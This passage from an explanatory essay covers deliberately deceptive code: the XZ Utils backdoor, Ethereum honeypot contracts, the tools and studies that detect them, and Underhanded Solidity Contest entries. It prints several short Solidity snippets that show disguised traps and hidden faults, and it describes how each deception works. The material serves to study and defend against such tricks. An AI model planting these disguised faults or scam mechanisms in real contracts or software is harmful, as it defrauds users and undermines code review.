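The inner step produces a new compiler whose machine code differs from A's, because T translates programs in its own way. But if T works correctly, the new compiler does what s specifies, which is also what A is supposed to do. Compiling s again with the new compiler should therefore produce exactly the same bytes as A. If A contains Thompson's changes, the bytes will differ. The method requires the compiler under test to always produce the same output from the same input, as most compilers do. Wheeler proved that the method works under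 stated assumptions, then tried it on four compilers, including GCC and a small Lisp compiler that he had deliberately corrupted.

The test works even if T, the second compiler, is malicious, as long as T contains nothing that affects this particular test. To defeat the test, an attacker would have to corrupt both compilers in compatible ways, and the defender can choose T after the attack has taken place.

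A match shows only that the compiler's source accurately describes the compiler. Wheeler mentions that in 2016 Microsoft's Visual Studio turned out to be quietly adding data-reporting calls to the programs it compiled, which his method would not normally detect. Somebody still has to read the source, and the check makes that reading worthwhile if the reader knows which files count as source.

### A backdoor in the test files

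XZ Utils is a set of free compression tools that most Linux systems include. Someone using the name Jia Tan began contributing to it in 2021 and gradually won the trust of its overworked maintainer, Lasse Collin, and the right to publish releases. In February and March 2024, Tan released two versions that contained a backdoor hidden in files that people don't usually read.

The payload was compiled code hidden in two of the project's test files. A compression library is tested on strange and damaged files, so nobody expects to be able to read them. The instructions for extracting the payload were in a build script, which prepares a program for compilation. Tan put the altered script in the packaged release that Linux distributors download but not in the public repository where developers review changes, so someone reading all the code in the repository would not have found the step that activated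 the attack.

The script also checked its environment, much as some Ethereum honeypots check which network they are running on. It installed the payload only when a package was being built for certain common Linux systems. The target was OpenSSH, the standard program for logging in to a Linux machine remotely. OpenSSH doesn't use XZ itself, but several Linux distributions had modified it to work with another component that loads the XZ library. Reading the OpenSSH source would therefore not have revealed the payload. Double-compiling would not have helped either, because even an uncompromised compiler would have built the code that the altered script supplied.

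On an infected machine, the attacker could run any command by sending a login request with the right digital signature, which only the holder of a secret key could produce. A tester could have sent random requests for years without setting off this data-triggered branch.

Tan also planted at least one disguise that would have done well in the Underhanded C Contest. One build script compiles a few lines of code to test whether the system supports a security feature that restricts what a program can do. Tan added a stray period to those lines so that they could never compile, and the script therefore always treated the feature as unsupported and left it out.

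Andres Freund, a Microsoft engineer who works on the PostgreSQL database, found the backdoor by accident while measuring the performance of his own software. Remote logins were using a surprising amount of processor time and taking about half a second longer than usual. He also remembered odd memory errors in earlier tests. He traced the delay to the XZ library, then to the test files and the build script, and published his findings on March 29, 2024. The infected versions had reached test releases of Debian and Fedora, among others, but not the stable versions of the major distributions, which run most servers.

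Measurement exposed this attack, as it had exposed Volkswagen's cheating, and in both cases somebody read the code closely only after the numbers looked wrong. But Freund was luckier than the West Virginia researchers. Volkswagen's hidden mode caused the pollution, so anyone who measured emissions on the road could detect it. The slow logins came from the code that installed the backdoor in memory, not from the backdoor's use, so a more efficient version would have left Freund no delay to measure.

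## Ethereum honeypots, 2017 and 2018

Jia Tan hid the XZ backdoor in files that few people read. A few years earlier, swindlers on the Ethereum blockchain had published disguised code, hoping that skilled people would study it.

Ethereum is a public ledger maintained by a network of computers. Its currency is ether, which programs count in wei, with 10^18 wei to one ether. Some accounts belong to people, who control them with secret keys, and others belong to smart contracts. A contract's account holds ether, the contract's code and its data. Nobody can change the code once it is on the ledger, and ether leaves the account only if the code sends it. To use a contract, a person sends a transaction that calls one of its functions and may include a payment. If the function stops with an error, the network undoes the whole transaction, including the payment, and keeps only a fee.

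Most authors write contracts in Solidity, which a compiler translates into bytecode. The blockchain stores only the bytecode. Readers who want the source code usually go to Etherscan, a website that displays Ethereum's accounts, transactions and contracts. An author can upload source code there, and Etherscan confirms that it compiles to the bytecode at the contract's address. Visitors can leave comments on a contract's page.

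### Bait for people who read code

By 2017, thieves knew they could profit by finding faults in smart contracts. Two attacks on faulty contracts, the DAO hack of 2016 and the Parity wallet hack of 2017, had together caused more than $400 million in losses. Thieves could also use the tools that researchers built to find such faults. *The Art of The Scam* (Ferreira Torres, Steichen and State, 2019), the first systematic study of honeypot contracts, describes how swindlers took advantage of this search for faulty code.

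The fraud has three phases. The creator puts the contract on the blockchain with some ether in it as bait. A victim notices the apparent flaw, sends the ether needed to exploit it and gets nothing back. The creator then withdraws both the bait and the victim's ether. Any Ethereum user with enough ether for the bait and the transaction fees can do this.

The creator of a honeypot wants the reader to find an apparent flaw and then stop reading, whereas an entrant in the Underhanded C Contest wanted the reader to find nothing wrong. The trap works only on people who can read Solidity well enough to notice the bait. The security researcher Schmidt, in *Smart Contract Honeypots for Profit (and probably Fun)*, observed that these contracts almost always look like a beginner's work, and that it is still easy to con someone who thinks they are the conman. Creators often uploaded the source code to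 Etherscan to make the supposed flaw easier to find, according to *A Data Science Approach for Honeypot Detection in Ethereum* (2019). Ivanov, Lou and colleagues (2021), in *Targeting the Weakest Link*, attribute the traps' success to confirmation bias, because experienced hackers overlook evidence that a contract isn't vulnerable once they believe that it is.

A would-be thief sends money only after reasoning that the contract will pay back more, so these victims resemble DUPOC more than CUPOD. But their knowledge of Ethereum is less reliable than a sound proof system, and one false belief about how the code will run is enough to trap them.

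Ferreira Torres and colleagues collected 24 honeypots from public sources and found eight techniques in them. One exploits the virtual machine that runs the contracts, four exploit the Solidity compiler, and three exploit the limits of what Etherscan displayed.

### The virtual machine: a balance that has already changed

A contract named MultiplicatorX3 contains this function:

```solidity
function multiplicate(address adr) payable {
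    if (msg.value >= this.balance)
        adr.transfer(this.balance + msg.value);
}
```

Here `msg.value` is the payment that comes with the call, and `this.balance` is the ether in the contract. The function appears to return the payment and pay out the balance to anyone who sends at least as much as the contract holds. If the contract holds 1 ether, a reader expects to send 1 and receive 2.

However, the virtual machine adds the payment to the balance before it runs the function. When the function compares the two, the balance is already 2 ether. The payment is only 1 ether, so the function skips the transfer and ends. No error has occurred, so the network doesn't undo the transaction, and the victim's ether stays in the contract.

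A larger payment doesn't help. If the contract held *b* ether and the victim sends *v*, the condition is *v* ≥ *b* + *v*, which is true only if the contract was empty, and then there is nothing to steal. Ferreira Torres and colleagues call this trick balance disorder. They think the addition in the last line is there only to strengthen the reader's mistake, because adding the two amounts would make sense if the balance did not yet include the payment. The virtual machine follows its published rules, so a reader who knows them can see the trap in these three lines.

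### The compiler: two owners and a shrinking number

KingOfTheHill is presented as a contest in which the highest bidder can take the pot. This is a shortened version:

```solidity
contract Ownable {
    address owner = msg.sender;
    modifier onlyOwner { require(msg.sender == owner); _; }
}

contract KingOfTheHill is Ownable {
    address public owner;

    function () public payable {
        if (msg.value > jackpot) owner = msg.sender;
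        jackpot += msg.value;
    }
    function takeAll() public onlyOwner {
        msg.sender.transfer(this.balance);
    }
}
```

The words `is Ownable` copy the first contract's code into the second, a common practice called inheritance. The unnamed function runs when someone sends ether without calling a particular function. If the payment exceeds the jackpot, the sender becomes `owner`. The label `onlyOwner` on `takeAll` makes that function fail for anyone except `owner`.

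A reader who checks the comparison for balance disorder will find that it works, because `jackpot` grows only afterward, and the sender does become `owner`. But the code declares `owner` twice, and the compiler treats the two declarations as separate variables. The payment changes the one in KingOfTheHill, while `onlyOwner` checks the one in Ownable, which still contains the creator's address. The victim's call to `takeAll` therefore fails. KingOfTheHill's variable is marked `public`, so a victim who looked up the contract's owner would see their own address.

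In *以太坊蜜罐智能合约分析* ("Analysis of Ethereum honeypot smart contracts"), dawu and 0x7F (2018) of the Chinese security company Knownsec expose the same trick in another contract by renaming the variables `owner1` and `owner2`. They also show that the full version of KingOfTheHill made each new owner wait five days before taking the money. This delay looks like a normal rule of the game, but it kept victims from discovering the trap immediately.

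HackerNoon's *Hacking the Hackers* describes a third example, ICO_Hold, with two apparent flaws. Anyone can call its setup function and supposedly become the owner, and its withdrawal function never subtracts a withdrawal from the depositor's record. A thief could seemingly use both flaws to deposit 0.5 ether and withdraw it repeatedly until the contract was empty. Neither flaw helps the thief, because the ownership check again uses the other variable. HackerNoon objected to calling such contracts honeypots, since security teams use that word for decoys that help them detect intruders, and proposed "mousetraps" instead.

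Another technique used a compiler bug. DividendDistributorv3 lets investors withdraw more than they put in, which looks like an oversight. The withdrawal function passes four values to a second function, which makes the payment. One of them is an empty message, and the compiler skipped empty text in such a list, so each later value moved up one place:

| Parameter | Value in the source code | Value it received |
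|---|---|---|
| Amount | The withdrawal | The withdrawal |
| Message | Empty text | The victim's address |
| Recipient | The victim's address | The owner's address |
| Current owner | The owner's address | Zero |

The withdrawal therefore goes to the owner. A reader who didn't know about the bug could not learn this from the source code, however carefully they read it.

For_Test appears to repay several times any amount above 0.1 ether. Its loop counts upward and, on each pass, stores twice the counter's value as the amount to repay. It should continue until the counter reaches twice the payment in wei, but it stops early if a result is smaller than the previous one. The author declared the counter with `var`, so the compiler gave it the smallest type that fits its starting value of 0, which can only hold numbers up to 255. When the counter reaches 128, its double is too large for this type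 and becomes 0, so the loop stops and the contract repays 254 wei to a victim who sent more than 100,000,000,000,000,000 wei.

Dawu and 0x7F explained this trap but gave the repayment as 510 wei, twice 255. They noticed that the counter was limited to 255 but not that its double was limited too. The mistake makes no practical difference to the victim, but it came from specialists who knew the contract was a trap.

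The remaining compiler technique appears in guessing games. GuessNumber charges at least 0.1 ether for a guess and offers its whole balance to anyone who names a secret number from 1 to 10. The number is in a variable marked `private`, which looks like a beginner's mistake because anyone can read data stored on the blockchain. The victim looks up the number and bets on it. Before checking the guess, the contract saves the player's address and guess in a record, but the code never assigns that record its own place in storage. The compiler therefore puts it at the beginning of storage, where the secret number is, and the player's address overwrites the number. An address is an enormous number and the contract rejects guesses above 10, so the bet practically always loses.

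OpenAddressLottery uses the same fault but lets its owner trigger it. The contract assigns each player a 0 or a 1, and a 1 wins. If the owner calls a function labeled in a comment as being for testing, the faulty record overwrites the winning number with a multiple of seven. Until then the lottery can pay winners normally, so a record of past prizes would not show that it was safe. Ferreira Torres and colleagues note that some people may take such a contract for a fair lottery, so not every victim of a honeypot was trying to steal.

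### The explorer: code and events that Etherscan did not show

Gift_1_ETH gives its balance to anyone who knows a password. It also lets anyone who sends at least 1 ether set a new password if a certain flag is still false. A visible function can set the flag to true, which would lock the current password. A careful victim who checks Etherscan finds no calls to this function.

However, the creator has already called it from another contract without attaching any ether, which set the flag to true. Etherscan left such calls out of its list to make the page easier to use. The new password therefore has no effect, and the contract keeps the victim's ether. Ferreira Torres and colleagues call this a hidden state update. The published code is accurate and fairly easy to understand, but the victim is misled because one call is missing from the history Etherscan displays. The victim could have avoided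 the trap by reading the flag directly from the blockchain.

Private_Bank uses bait that experienced thieves would recognize from the DAO hack. This is its withdrawal function, slightly simplified:

```solidity
function CashOut(uint amount) {
    if (amount <= balances[msg.sender])
        if (msg.sender.call.value(amount)()) {
            balances[msg.sender] -= amount;
            TransferLog.AddMessage("CashOut");
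        }
}
```

The bank sends the money before it reduces the customer's recorded balance. If the customer is itself a contract, the payment triggers some of that contract's code, which can call `CashOut` again. The record still shows the full deposit, so the bank pays again. This attack, known as reentrancy, can repeat until the bank is empty. The thief must first make a minimum deposit.

The trap is in the last line of the function, which looks like routine bookkeeping. The published file includes a contract called Log, whose `AddMessage` function just saves a message. But the bank uses whatever contract is at the address its creator supplied at setup, and the contract there has a different `AddMessage`. That version raises an error if the message is "CashOut" and the caller isn't the creator.

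When the thief attacks, the bank sends the money, perhaps many times, and then calls the logger, which raises an error that undoes every payment in the transaction. The thief's deposit stays in the bank because it was made in an earlier transaction. An honest customer couldn't withdraw anything either. In *ethereum_better_honey_pot*, the programmer Sherbuck published a working teaching copy and compared it to a man-trap, because only the owner can remove ether once it has entered.

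Ferreira Torres and colleagues call this a straw man contract. Etherscan correctly confirmed that the bank's source matched its bytecode, but this check did not cover the contract at the other address. Each part could look correct by itself, like the two files in Åkesson's warhead program.

Dawu and 0x7F analyzed another version of the bank, which they found in a public collection of honeypots. They explained the reentrancy flaw, wrote an attack and tried it in a simulation, where the attacker recovered a deposit of 10 ether and took another customer's 50. They concluded that the danger to ordinary depositors was that an attacker would rob the bank. Their explanation doesn't mention the logger, and the attack could have succeeded only if the logger in their simulation was harmless. They appear to have stopped looking once they confirmed that the bait worked, even though they knew the contract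 was a honeypot.

Dawu and 0x7F did investigate the hidden code in a related contract, firstTest. Its code appears to send its balance to anyone who sends it more than 1 ether, but it first calls a logging function at another address. The call uses `delegatecall`, which lets the other contract's code change the caller's stored data. They translated the bytecode at that address back into readable form and found that the logging function replaces the recipient's address with that of firstTest, so the contract sends the money to itself.

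The simplest disguise was a long row of spaces. For some time, Etherscan displayed source code in a box that didn't wrap long lines, so readers had to scroll sideways to see the rest. The important part of WhaleGiveaway1 looked like this:

```solidity
if (msg.value > 1 ether)
{
    msg.sender.transfer(this.balance);
}
```

Another instruction, `Owner.transfer(this.balance);`, is far to the right, beyond the edge of the box. It runs first and sends the contract's entire balance to the owner. The visible instruction then sends the victim the remaining balance, which is zero. An editor that wraps long lines shows the hidden instruction.

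### A trap that recognizes a test

TestToken, another contract with hidden code, was also designed to account for people who tested it. Developers can try out contracts on test networks, which work like Ethereum but use worthless ether. A cautious thief could copy the contract to one of these networks and rehearse the theft.

Blockchains add transactions in numbered batches called blocks, and the test networks had not yet reached the main network's block numbers. The hidden code in TestToken checks whether the current block number is greater than 5,040,270. If it is, as it is on the main network, the code raises an error for everyone but the owner, and the money that the victim paid in earlier stays in the contract. On a test network the number is lower, so a victim who tries the theft there first sees the visible code run and pay out the whole balance.

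TestToken's concealed defection branch is triggered by its environment in almost the same way as Volkswagen's. Volkswagen's software used sensors and distance curves to recognize a test, while TestToken needed only one comparison with a number that every contract can look up.

A better rehearsal uses a private copy of the main network. Murdoch and Paterno, in *Pentesting Ethereum Contracts*, a workshop at the developer conference Devcon 5, taught developers to make such a copy and try a reentrancy attack on a real honeypot without risking any money. The copy has the main network's block number, the flag that the creator secretly changed and the logger that the bank really uses. Running the planned theft on it should therefore expose all eight techniques, even if the thief understands none of them. (Later swindlers built traps for bots that do simulate their transactions first.)

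Ivanov and colleagues showed that such disguises could also endanger people who weren't trying to steal. They devised six attacks that stay inactive during testing and start only in the final version, and added them to the code of five popular contracts without changing what the contracts normally did. In one attack, every withdrawal first sends a small fee to what looks like the owner's personal account. The attacker later replaces that account's address with the address of a contract that can't accept payments. The two addresses differ by only one character or two swapped characters. The fee payment then fails, which blocks the customer's withdrawal.

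Ethereum addresses have a checksum to catch typing errors, but the researchers needed only seconds to find two similar addresses that both passed. They also searched 85,656 published contracts and found 1,027 that someone could use for such attacks. Expert opinions from seven security firms supported the view that the attacks were dangerous. The study showed that the attacks were possible but did not count victims.

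Some traps involve no quirk of Ethereum. In RACEFORETH, which dawu and 0x7F describe and which isn't among the eight techniques, players win a prize once their payments total 100 finney, or 0.1 ether. A player's first payment can be at most 50 finney, and the limit halves after each payment. The code does what a reader would expect, but no one can win, because the most a player can pay is 50 + 25 + 12.5 and so on, which approaches 100 but never reaches it.

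### Victims, timing and profits

Ferreira Torres and colleagues searched about two million contracts from August 2015 to October 2018 with their detection tool, HoneyBadger, and confirmed 282 honeypots by reading the source code. They then went through the transactions of these 282 to find out who had lost money. The slides with which Ferreira Torres and colleagues presented the study give the results for each technique:

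| Technique | Layer | Confirmed honeypots | Honeypots with a victim |
|---|---|---|---|
| Balance disorder | Virtual machine | 20 | 7 |
| Inheritance disorder | Compiler | 41 | 17 |
| Skipped empty text | Compiler | 9 | 7 |
| Number type too small | Compiler | 4 | 1 |
| Record without its own storage | Compiler | 32 | 11 |
| Hidden state update | Etherscan | 134 | 49 |
| Straw man contract | Etherscan | 30 | 8 |
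| Hidden transfer | Etherscan | 12 | 3 |
| **Total** | | **282** | **103** |

About 37% of the honeypots caught someone. Creators emptied another 54% without catching anyone, and the remaining 10% still held bait. The compiler bug that skipped empty text had the highest success rate, 78%. That is plausible for a trap that source code alone can't reveal, but nine contracts are too few for a firm comparison. The three Etherscan techniques made up 62% of the honeypots, so most creators relied at least partly on gaps in what the website showed. A better display would have helped their victims more than better knowledge of Solidity.

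The success rate doesn't measure how often readers spotted the traps, because the blockchain records payments but not people who read the code and sent no money. A honeypot with no victims may have had a hundred readers who all recognized it, or no readers. The figures do show that people with their own money at risk misread the code.

The study identified 240 victims, counting each address as one. Of the successful honeypots, 71% caught a single victim, while one caught 97. Eight victims fell for more than one honeypot, including one who fell for four. Fifty-three creators set up at least two honeypots each, and 42 of them used the same type each time.

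Thieves moved quickly. The fastest attempt came 7 minutes and 37 seconds after a honeypot appeared. Half of the first attempts came within 16 hours, and about 55% within 24 hours. This haste may have helped the traps work, because anyone who found an apparently unprotected balance had reason to fear that another thief would take it first, and so had little time to look for a second problem.

Ferreira Torres and colleagues suggest that most honeypots caught only one person because later readers checked the earlier transactions and saw what had happened. That is reasonable, but creators also tended to withdraw everything within a day of a victim's payment, leaving no money to attract anyone else. The data can't distinguish between these explanations.

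Public warnings seem to have helped. Etherscan users had commented on 87 of the honeypots, mostly to warn that the contract might be a trap. Twenty of the 87 (23%) caught someone, compared with 43% of those without comments. Sixteen of the 20 had succeeded before the first comment, and four succeeded even after a comment had appeared on the same website that displayed the code. After 21 of the comments, creators withdrew the bait, usually within about a day.

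The total profit was 257.25 ether, worth $90,118 at the times of withdrawal. Honeypots that used hidden state updates earned two thirds of it. The median profit was about 1 ether, roughly what many of these contracts required a victim to pay for one attempt. The largest profit in dollars was $2,609. Only one contract of For_Test's type is known to have caught a victim, and it cost its creator more in fees than it earned.

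Ferreira Torres and colleagues describe their totals as lower bounds. They could confirm only contracts with published source code, they searched for only eight techniques, and their data ended in October 2018. Zhou, Yang and colleagues, in *An Ever-evolving Game*, searched 420 million transactions up to March 2019 for contracts that received payments and paid out only to their creators. They found 141 honeypots that had taken money from victims, 51 of which the earlier study had missed. A few of the new ones, which they call "racing time", offered high interest on deposits but left almost no time, or none, to withdraw them.

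The victims in this second study lost 427 ether, worth $80,866. This total can't be compared directly with the earlier profit because it doesn't subtract the creators' costs and uses different conversion dates. It is also probably too low, since Zhou and colleagues found 16 more honeypots, disguised as banks, that their method had missed.

The earlier study also made an error in the opposite direction, counting some contracts that were not honeypots. Zhou and colleagues found that users could profit from 15 of the 282 contracts it counted. Thirteen were genuine lotteries or roulette games, so some of the 240 victims may have been unlucky gamblers. The other two were honeypots that their creators had set up incorrectly, and anyone who guessed the password could take the money left as bait.

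## Automated honeypot detection and changes to Solidity, 2017 to 2022

The study that confirmed 282 honeypots began with two million contracts. Removing exact copies left 151,935 different programs, most without published source code. That was still too many to read, so Ferreira Torres and colleagues wrote HoneyBadger, a tool that searches bytecode. Compilation removes comments, misleading names and long rows of spaces, so disguises that rely on them don't appear in bytecode. It also removes some useful information, such as which contract inherited code from which.

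### Payments that can't happen

HoneyBadger relies on symbolic execution. It divides the bytecode into blocks of instructions that always run together, and maps which blocks can lead to which others. It then follows the paths through this map, treating the payment, the caller's address and the stored data as unknowns. Every branch adds a condition on these unknowns, and the Z3 solver looks for values that meet all the conditions on a path. If none exist, no transaction can take that path.

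Tools of this kind normally skip impossible paths to save time, but HoneyBadger follows them because a honeypot's bait may be a payment that can never happen.

A honeypot has to take in the victim's money and later pay it out to the creator. HoneyBadger therefore keeps only contracts where it finds both a path that accepts a payment above zero and a way for ether to leave. This filter passed 48,487 contracts, or 32%. The tool then applies one rule for each of the eight known techniques.

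HoneyBadger reports a balance disorder if an unreachable block contains a transfer equal to the caller's payment plus the contract's balance. MultiplicatorX3 meets both conditions. Its transfer runs only if *v* ≥ *b* + *v*, where *b* is the bait and *v* is the caller's payment. No payment can satisfy this while there is bait in the contract, so the block containing the transfer is unreachable. The amount in that transfer is `this.balance + msg.value`, which matches the sum in the rule.

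The rule should raise few false alarms, because an honest programmer has little reason to offer a contract's entire balance in code that can't run. But the rule as Ferreira Torres and colleagues state it is narrow, and would not match a copy that promised the balance plus twice the payment.

Some other rules have to rely on indirect signs. Bytecode doesn't show that KingOfTheHill has two variables named `owner`, so HoneyBadger looks for a function that stores the caller's address where no later check or payment uses it, together with a payment that requires the caller to match an address stored elsewhere. For a hidden state update, it looks for a payment that depends on a stored value that another function can change without moving any money. Gift_1_ETH fits that description, but so would an honest contract with an on-off switch.

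### What the 87 percent measures

HoneyBadger flagged 460 of the 151,935 contracts. Ferreira Torres and colleagues found source code for 323 of them, read it, and confirmed 282 as honeypots, a precision of 87%.

| Technique | Flagged, with source code | Confirmed | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Balance disorder | 20 | 20 | 100% |
| Inheritance disorder | 48 | 41 | 85% |
| Skipped empty text | 9 | 9 | 100% |
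| Number type too small | 4 | 4 | 100% |
| Record without its own storage | 32 | 32 | 100% |
| Hidden state update | 164 | 134 | 82% |
| Straw man contract | 34 | 30 | 88% |
| Hidden transfer | 12 | 12 | 100% |
| **Total** | **323** | **282** | **87%** |

The study uses "false positive rate" for the share of alarms that were wrong, which was 18% for hidden state updates. HoneyBadger flagged a far smaller share of honest contracts, 41 of about 151,600, or 0.03%. That share would be only 0.12% even if every flagged contract without source code was also honest. Honeypots are so rare that this share has to be very low for most alarms to be right. A tool that caught the same 282 honeypots but flagged 1% of honest contracts would have raised about 1,500 false alarms, and only one alarm in six would have been right.

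The 87% is probably a little too high. The researchers were checking their own tool, and they looked in the source code for the same features that their rules describe. Their 460 contracts also included the 24 examples they had used to identify the eight techniques. If the 13 lotteries and roulette games that Zhou and colleagues later found among the 282 count as false alarms, the precision falls to 83%.

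Precision doesn't measure how many honeypots HoneyBadger missed. The tool has no rule for RACEFORETH, for example, whose players can never pay in enough to win. Its detection rate was roughly 64%, based on the earlier study having found 90 of the 141 honeypots that Zhou and colleagues listed as having taken money. But their data ran five months longer, so some of the other 51 may not have existed when HoneyBadger was run.

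### Judging a contract by its money

Somebody has to discover a trick before anyone can write a rule to detect it. Camino, Torres and colleagues (2019), in *A Data Science Approach for Detecting Honeypots in Ethereum*, instead looked for a pattern of payments that honeypots should share however they are disguised. The creator should put in the bait, victims should add more money, and only the creator should take any out.

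For each transaction, the researchers recorded whether the creator or somebody else sent it, whether it created the contract, whether it failed, and whose balance went up or down. These details can combine in 864 ways, of which 244 make sense and 74 occurred in the data. The researchers calculated how often each combination occurred in each contract's transactions. They added other facts about the transactions, such as their number and average value, and a few about the contract's source code, such as its length and compiler version. The data covered 295 honeypots (HoneyBadger's confirmed finds and some exact copies) and 158,568 other contracts with published source code.

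XGBoost, a machine-learning program, then built a series of decision trees, each correcting the errors of the earlier ones, and used them to estimate the probability that each contract was a honeypot. On contracts left out of training, it scored 0.968 on a standard measure called AUROC. This means it would rate a randomly chosen honeypot as more suspicious than a randomly chosen non-honeypot about 97% of the time. The most useful feature by far was how often the creator simply paid ether into the contract.

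The researchers also tested whether the model could detect honeypots that used a technique missing from its training data. In each of eight tests, they removed every honeypot of one technique, trained the model on the rest of the data and then ran it on the removed contracts. The model found 28 of the 31 straw man contracts. Its worst result was 17 of 20, for balance disorder, and across all eight tests it found 269 of 295, or 91%.

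That is good evidence that different disguises leave similar traces in the transactions. It is weaker evidence about undiscovered tricks, because HoneyBadger's rules originally picked out all 295 contracts. The tests also included no honest contracts, so they could not measure a false positive rate to go with the 91%.

In a more practical trial, the researchers used the model to rank the remaining contracts, read the 100 scored as most suspicious, and found 57 new honeypots. Fifty of these used tricks that HoneyBadger already had rules for, including 16 hidden state updates and 13 cases of inheritance disorder. HoneyBadger's detection rate for its own eight tricks was therefore at most about 85% among contracts with published source code. The true rate may be much lower, since nobody read the contracts further down the list.

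The other seven used two new tricks. In six of them, the bait is a payment with its last two characters missing:

```solidity
msg.sender.call.value(amount);      // only prepares a payment
msg.sender.call.value(amount)();    // makes the payment
```

A person reading the source code sees a payment that will never happen. Most compiler versions remove the useless code that prepares it, so the bytecode contains no payment for HoneyBadger to examine.

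The seventh contract stores its owner's address under the key "Stephen". Anyone who pays can call a setup function that seems to replace this address with their own. But the second "e" of "Stephen" in that function is a Cyrillic letter that looks the same, so the function stores the new address under a different key and the owner never changes. Look-alike characters were also the second most common trick among the vote-counting programs of 2004.

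A method based on transactions can't classify a contract that has none. Some of the evidence appears only after a victim has paid, and half of the first attempted thefts came within 16 hours. The creator's deposit is available earlier, but a swindler could make it from a second account. The model scored almost as well, 0.942, with the source code features alone, but it relied mainly on the number of lines and the compiler version, which a swindler can easily change.

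Honeypots also varied more than the theory predicted. About 10% had received no deposit from the creator's account, and some of these used money from the first victims to attract others. About 17% had paid somebody other than the creator. In one case the creator forgot to make the hidden call that sets the trap, and the intended victims made a profit.

Torres, Baden and State, in *Towards Usable Protection Against Honeypots*, built a plug-in for the MetaMask wallet that consults HoneyBadger before the user pays. A server analyzes every new contract, and the wallet displays a warning or an approval. HoneyBadger's median analysis took 31 seconds, while the fastest known attempt on a honeypot came after more than seven minutes, so the result would usually be ready in time. The paper gives no new accuracy figures. The approval would also appear for every honeypot that HoneyBadger misses, which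 could reassure a victim who had begun to have doubts.

### Sneaking a fault past Solidity's developers

While swindlers were setting these traps, Solidity programmers held contests for writing code with disguised faults. Nick Johnson organized the first in 2017 and modeled it on Craver's contest. Its theme was the initial coin offering, in which a project raises money by selling new digital tokens. Under the rules, reproduced in Stalder's *Underhanded Solidity Coding Contest* (2017), entrants had to write a contract that would pass a careful audit but let the project's founders take the investors' money. As in Craver's contest, bugs that could pass as honest mistakes earned more points. Christian Reitwiessner, Solidity's lead developer, was one of the judges.

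Martin Swende won by exploiting the way the compiler handled encoded arrays, according to ConsenSys Diligence's *2nd Solidity Underhanded Contest* (2020). Richard Moore came second with a contract that has no fault in its code. It sells tokens for ether, one for one, and limits how quickly the owner can withdraw the proceeds:

```solidity
uint256 maxAmount = (_totalSupply - this.balance + (1 ether));
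```

The token supply equals all the ether buyers have paid in. Subtracting the current balance gives the amount the owner has already withdrawn, and the formula allows that amount again plus 1 ether. The owner can therefore take 1 ether in the first week, then 2, 4, 8 and so on. The formula works as long as the balance never exceeds the supply, which the code seems to guarantee.

But the owner can calculate the contract's address and send ether there before the contract exists, when no code can refuse it or issue tokens for it. In Moore's demonstration in *Underhanded Solidity Contest Entry*, buyers had paid 89.70324 ether, but the contract held 92.84483. The formula then gives 89.70324 − 92.84483 + 1, or −2.14159. A `uint256` can't hold a negative number, so the result wraps around to a very large positive one, and the owner can withdraw everything at once.

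The trigger is the contract's starting balance, which is outside the code and which the owner sets before putting the program on the blockchain. Moore hinted to the judges that the contract's code "is actually correct (and safe)". A reader could check every line and still miss the attack by assuming that a new contract starts with an empty account. Symbolic execution could find it if the tool treated the starting balance as an unknown.

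### Upgrades and hidden characters

The Solidity team revived the contest in 2020. Its aims included uncovering flaws in the language's design and testing recently added features and restrictions (Solidity, 2020). The theme was upgrades. Nobody can change a contract's code, so developers who want to fix bugs later often have one contract pass its calls to another, while keeping the power to replace the second. One entrant who received an honorable mention objected that auditing such a contract is pointless unless somebody also checks every upgrade.

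Robert Forster's winning contract delays each upgrade by a month so that users can react. Its only suspicious feature was that it stores the upgrade date as a day and a month. Heintel (2020) explains in *Announcing the Winners of the Underhanded Solidity Contest* that Forster put invisible characters in a comment to change the direction of the text. The comment marks `/*` and `*/` are mirror images, so the reversed text still looked like valid code, but the day and month were swapped. The upgrade could then happen much earlier than users expected. This was eleven months before Boucher and Anderson published the same kind of attack for eight other languages.

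In Jaime Iglesias's entry, which came second, an administrator can upgrade a token only if the owner has consented. The contract records this consent at a long storage address, which a comment falsely says is derived from a certain phrase. The address is actually where the contract stores the token balance of an account the administrator knows about. Any nonzero value counts as consent, so the administrator can unlock the upgrade by sending tokens to that account and lock it again by moving them out. A reviewer would have to redo the calculation in the comment to notice the mismatch.

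### An exchange that no judge could crack

Entrants in the 2022 contest had to write an exchange that looked fair but was open to manipulation. *Announcing the Winners of the Underhanded Solidity Contest 2022* (Heintel, 2022) reports that none of the judges could find the trick in the winning entry without reading its author's explanation.

The author, Tynan Richards, wrote an exchange for two kinds of token. Customers lend it tokens to trade with, and the fees from trading make this pool grow. The administrator may claim part of the growth and may change the size of that part. To protect the lenders, the contract is supposed to pay the administrator at the old rate before changing it, then block further claims for seven days so that anyone unhappy with the new rate can leave. ChainSecurity's *Beware of Undefined Behavior!* (2022) prints the code. This is a simplified version with different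 names:

```solidity
event RateChanged(uint256 indexed oldRate, uint256 indexed newRate);

function changeRate(uint256 newRate) external onlyAdmin {
    emit RateChanged(retireOldRate(), setNewRate(newRate));
}
function retireOldRate() internal returns (uint256) {
    payAdmin();                              // at the current rate
    nextClaim = block.timestamp + 7 days;    // then block further claims
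    return rate;
}
function setNewRate(uint256 newRate) internal returns (uint256) {
    rate = newRate;
    return newRate;
}
```

The `emit` line writes an entry in a public log and calls the other two functions to get the values to record. The compiler evaluates event values marked `indexed` from right to left, although Solidity doesn't specify an order and most readers will assume that the function on the left runs first. As a result, the new rate takes effect first, and the contract pays the administrator at that rate before the seven-day block begins.

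The code sets no maximum rate. Suppose the pool is worth 1,000 and has grown by 10 since the last claim. At a rate of 10%, the administrator would receive 1. By raising the rate to 10,000%, the administrator would receive 100 times the growth, or 1,000, which is the whole pool.

The judges found at least seven lesser weaknesses, such as missing protection against unfavorable prices, and these may have distracted them from the real one. Because the judges were experts who knew the contract was malicious, this is some of the clearest contest evidence that careful reading can fail. They added that a good unit test or a fuzzer would have found the fault. The log would also have revealed it, because the contract replaces the old rate before looking it up, so the entry shows the new rate twice.

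The trick also depends on how the author compiles the code. Solidity had an experimental compilation route that usually evaluates expressions from left to right, and ChainSecurity notes that the contract behaves as a reader would expect when compiled this way. A tester who used a different compiler setting from the author could have run the attack and seen it fail.

Michael Zhu's third-place entry combines the addresses of a collectible and a payment token into a single key for each bid. Reversing the order of the two addresses gives the same key, so a seller who swaps them can make the contract take a collectible from the bidder instead of the payment. A comment in the code misleads readers by stating, correctly, that a different pair with the same key is practically impossible to find.

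### What newer compilers prevent

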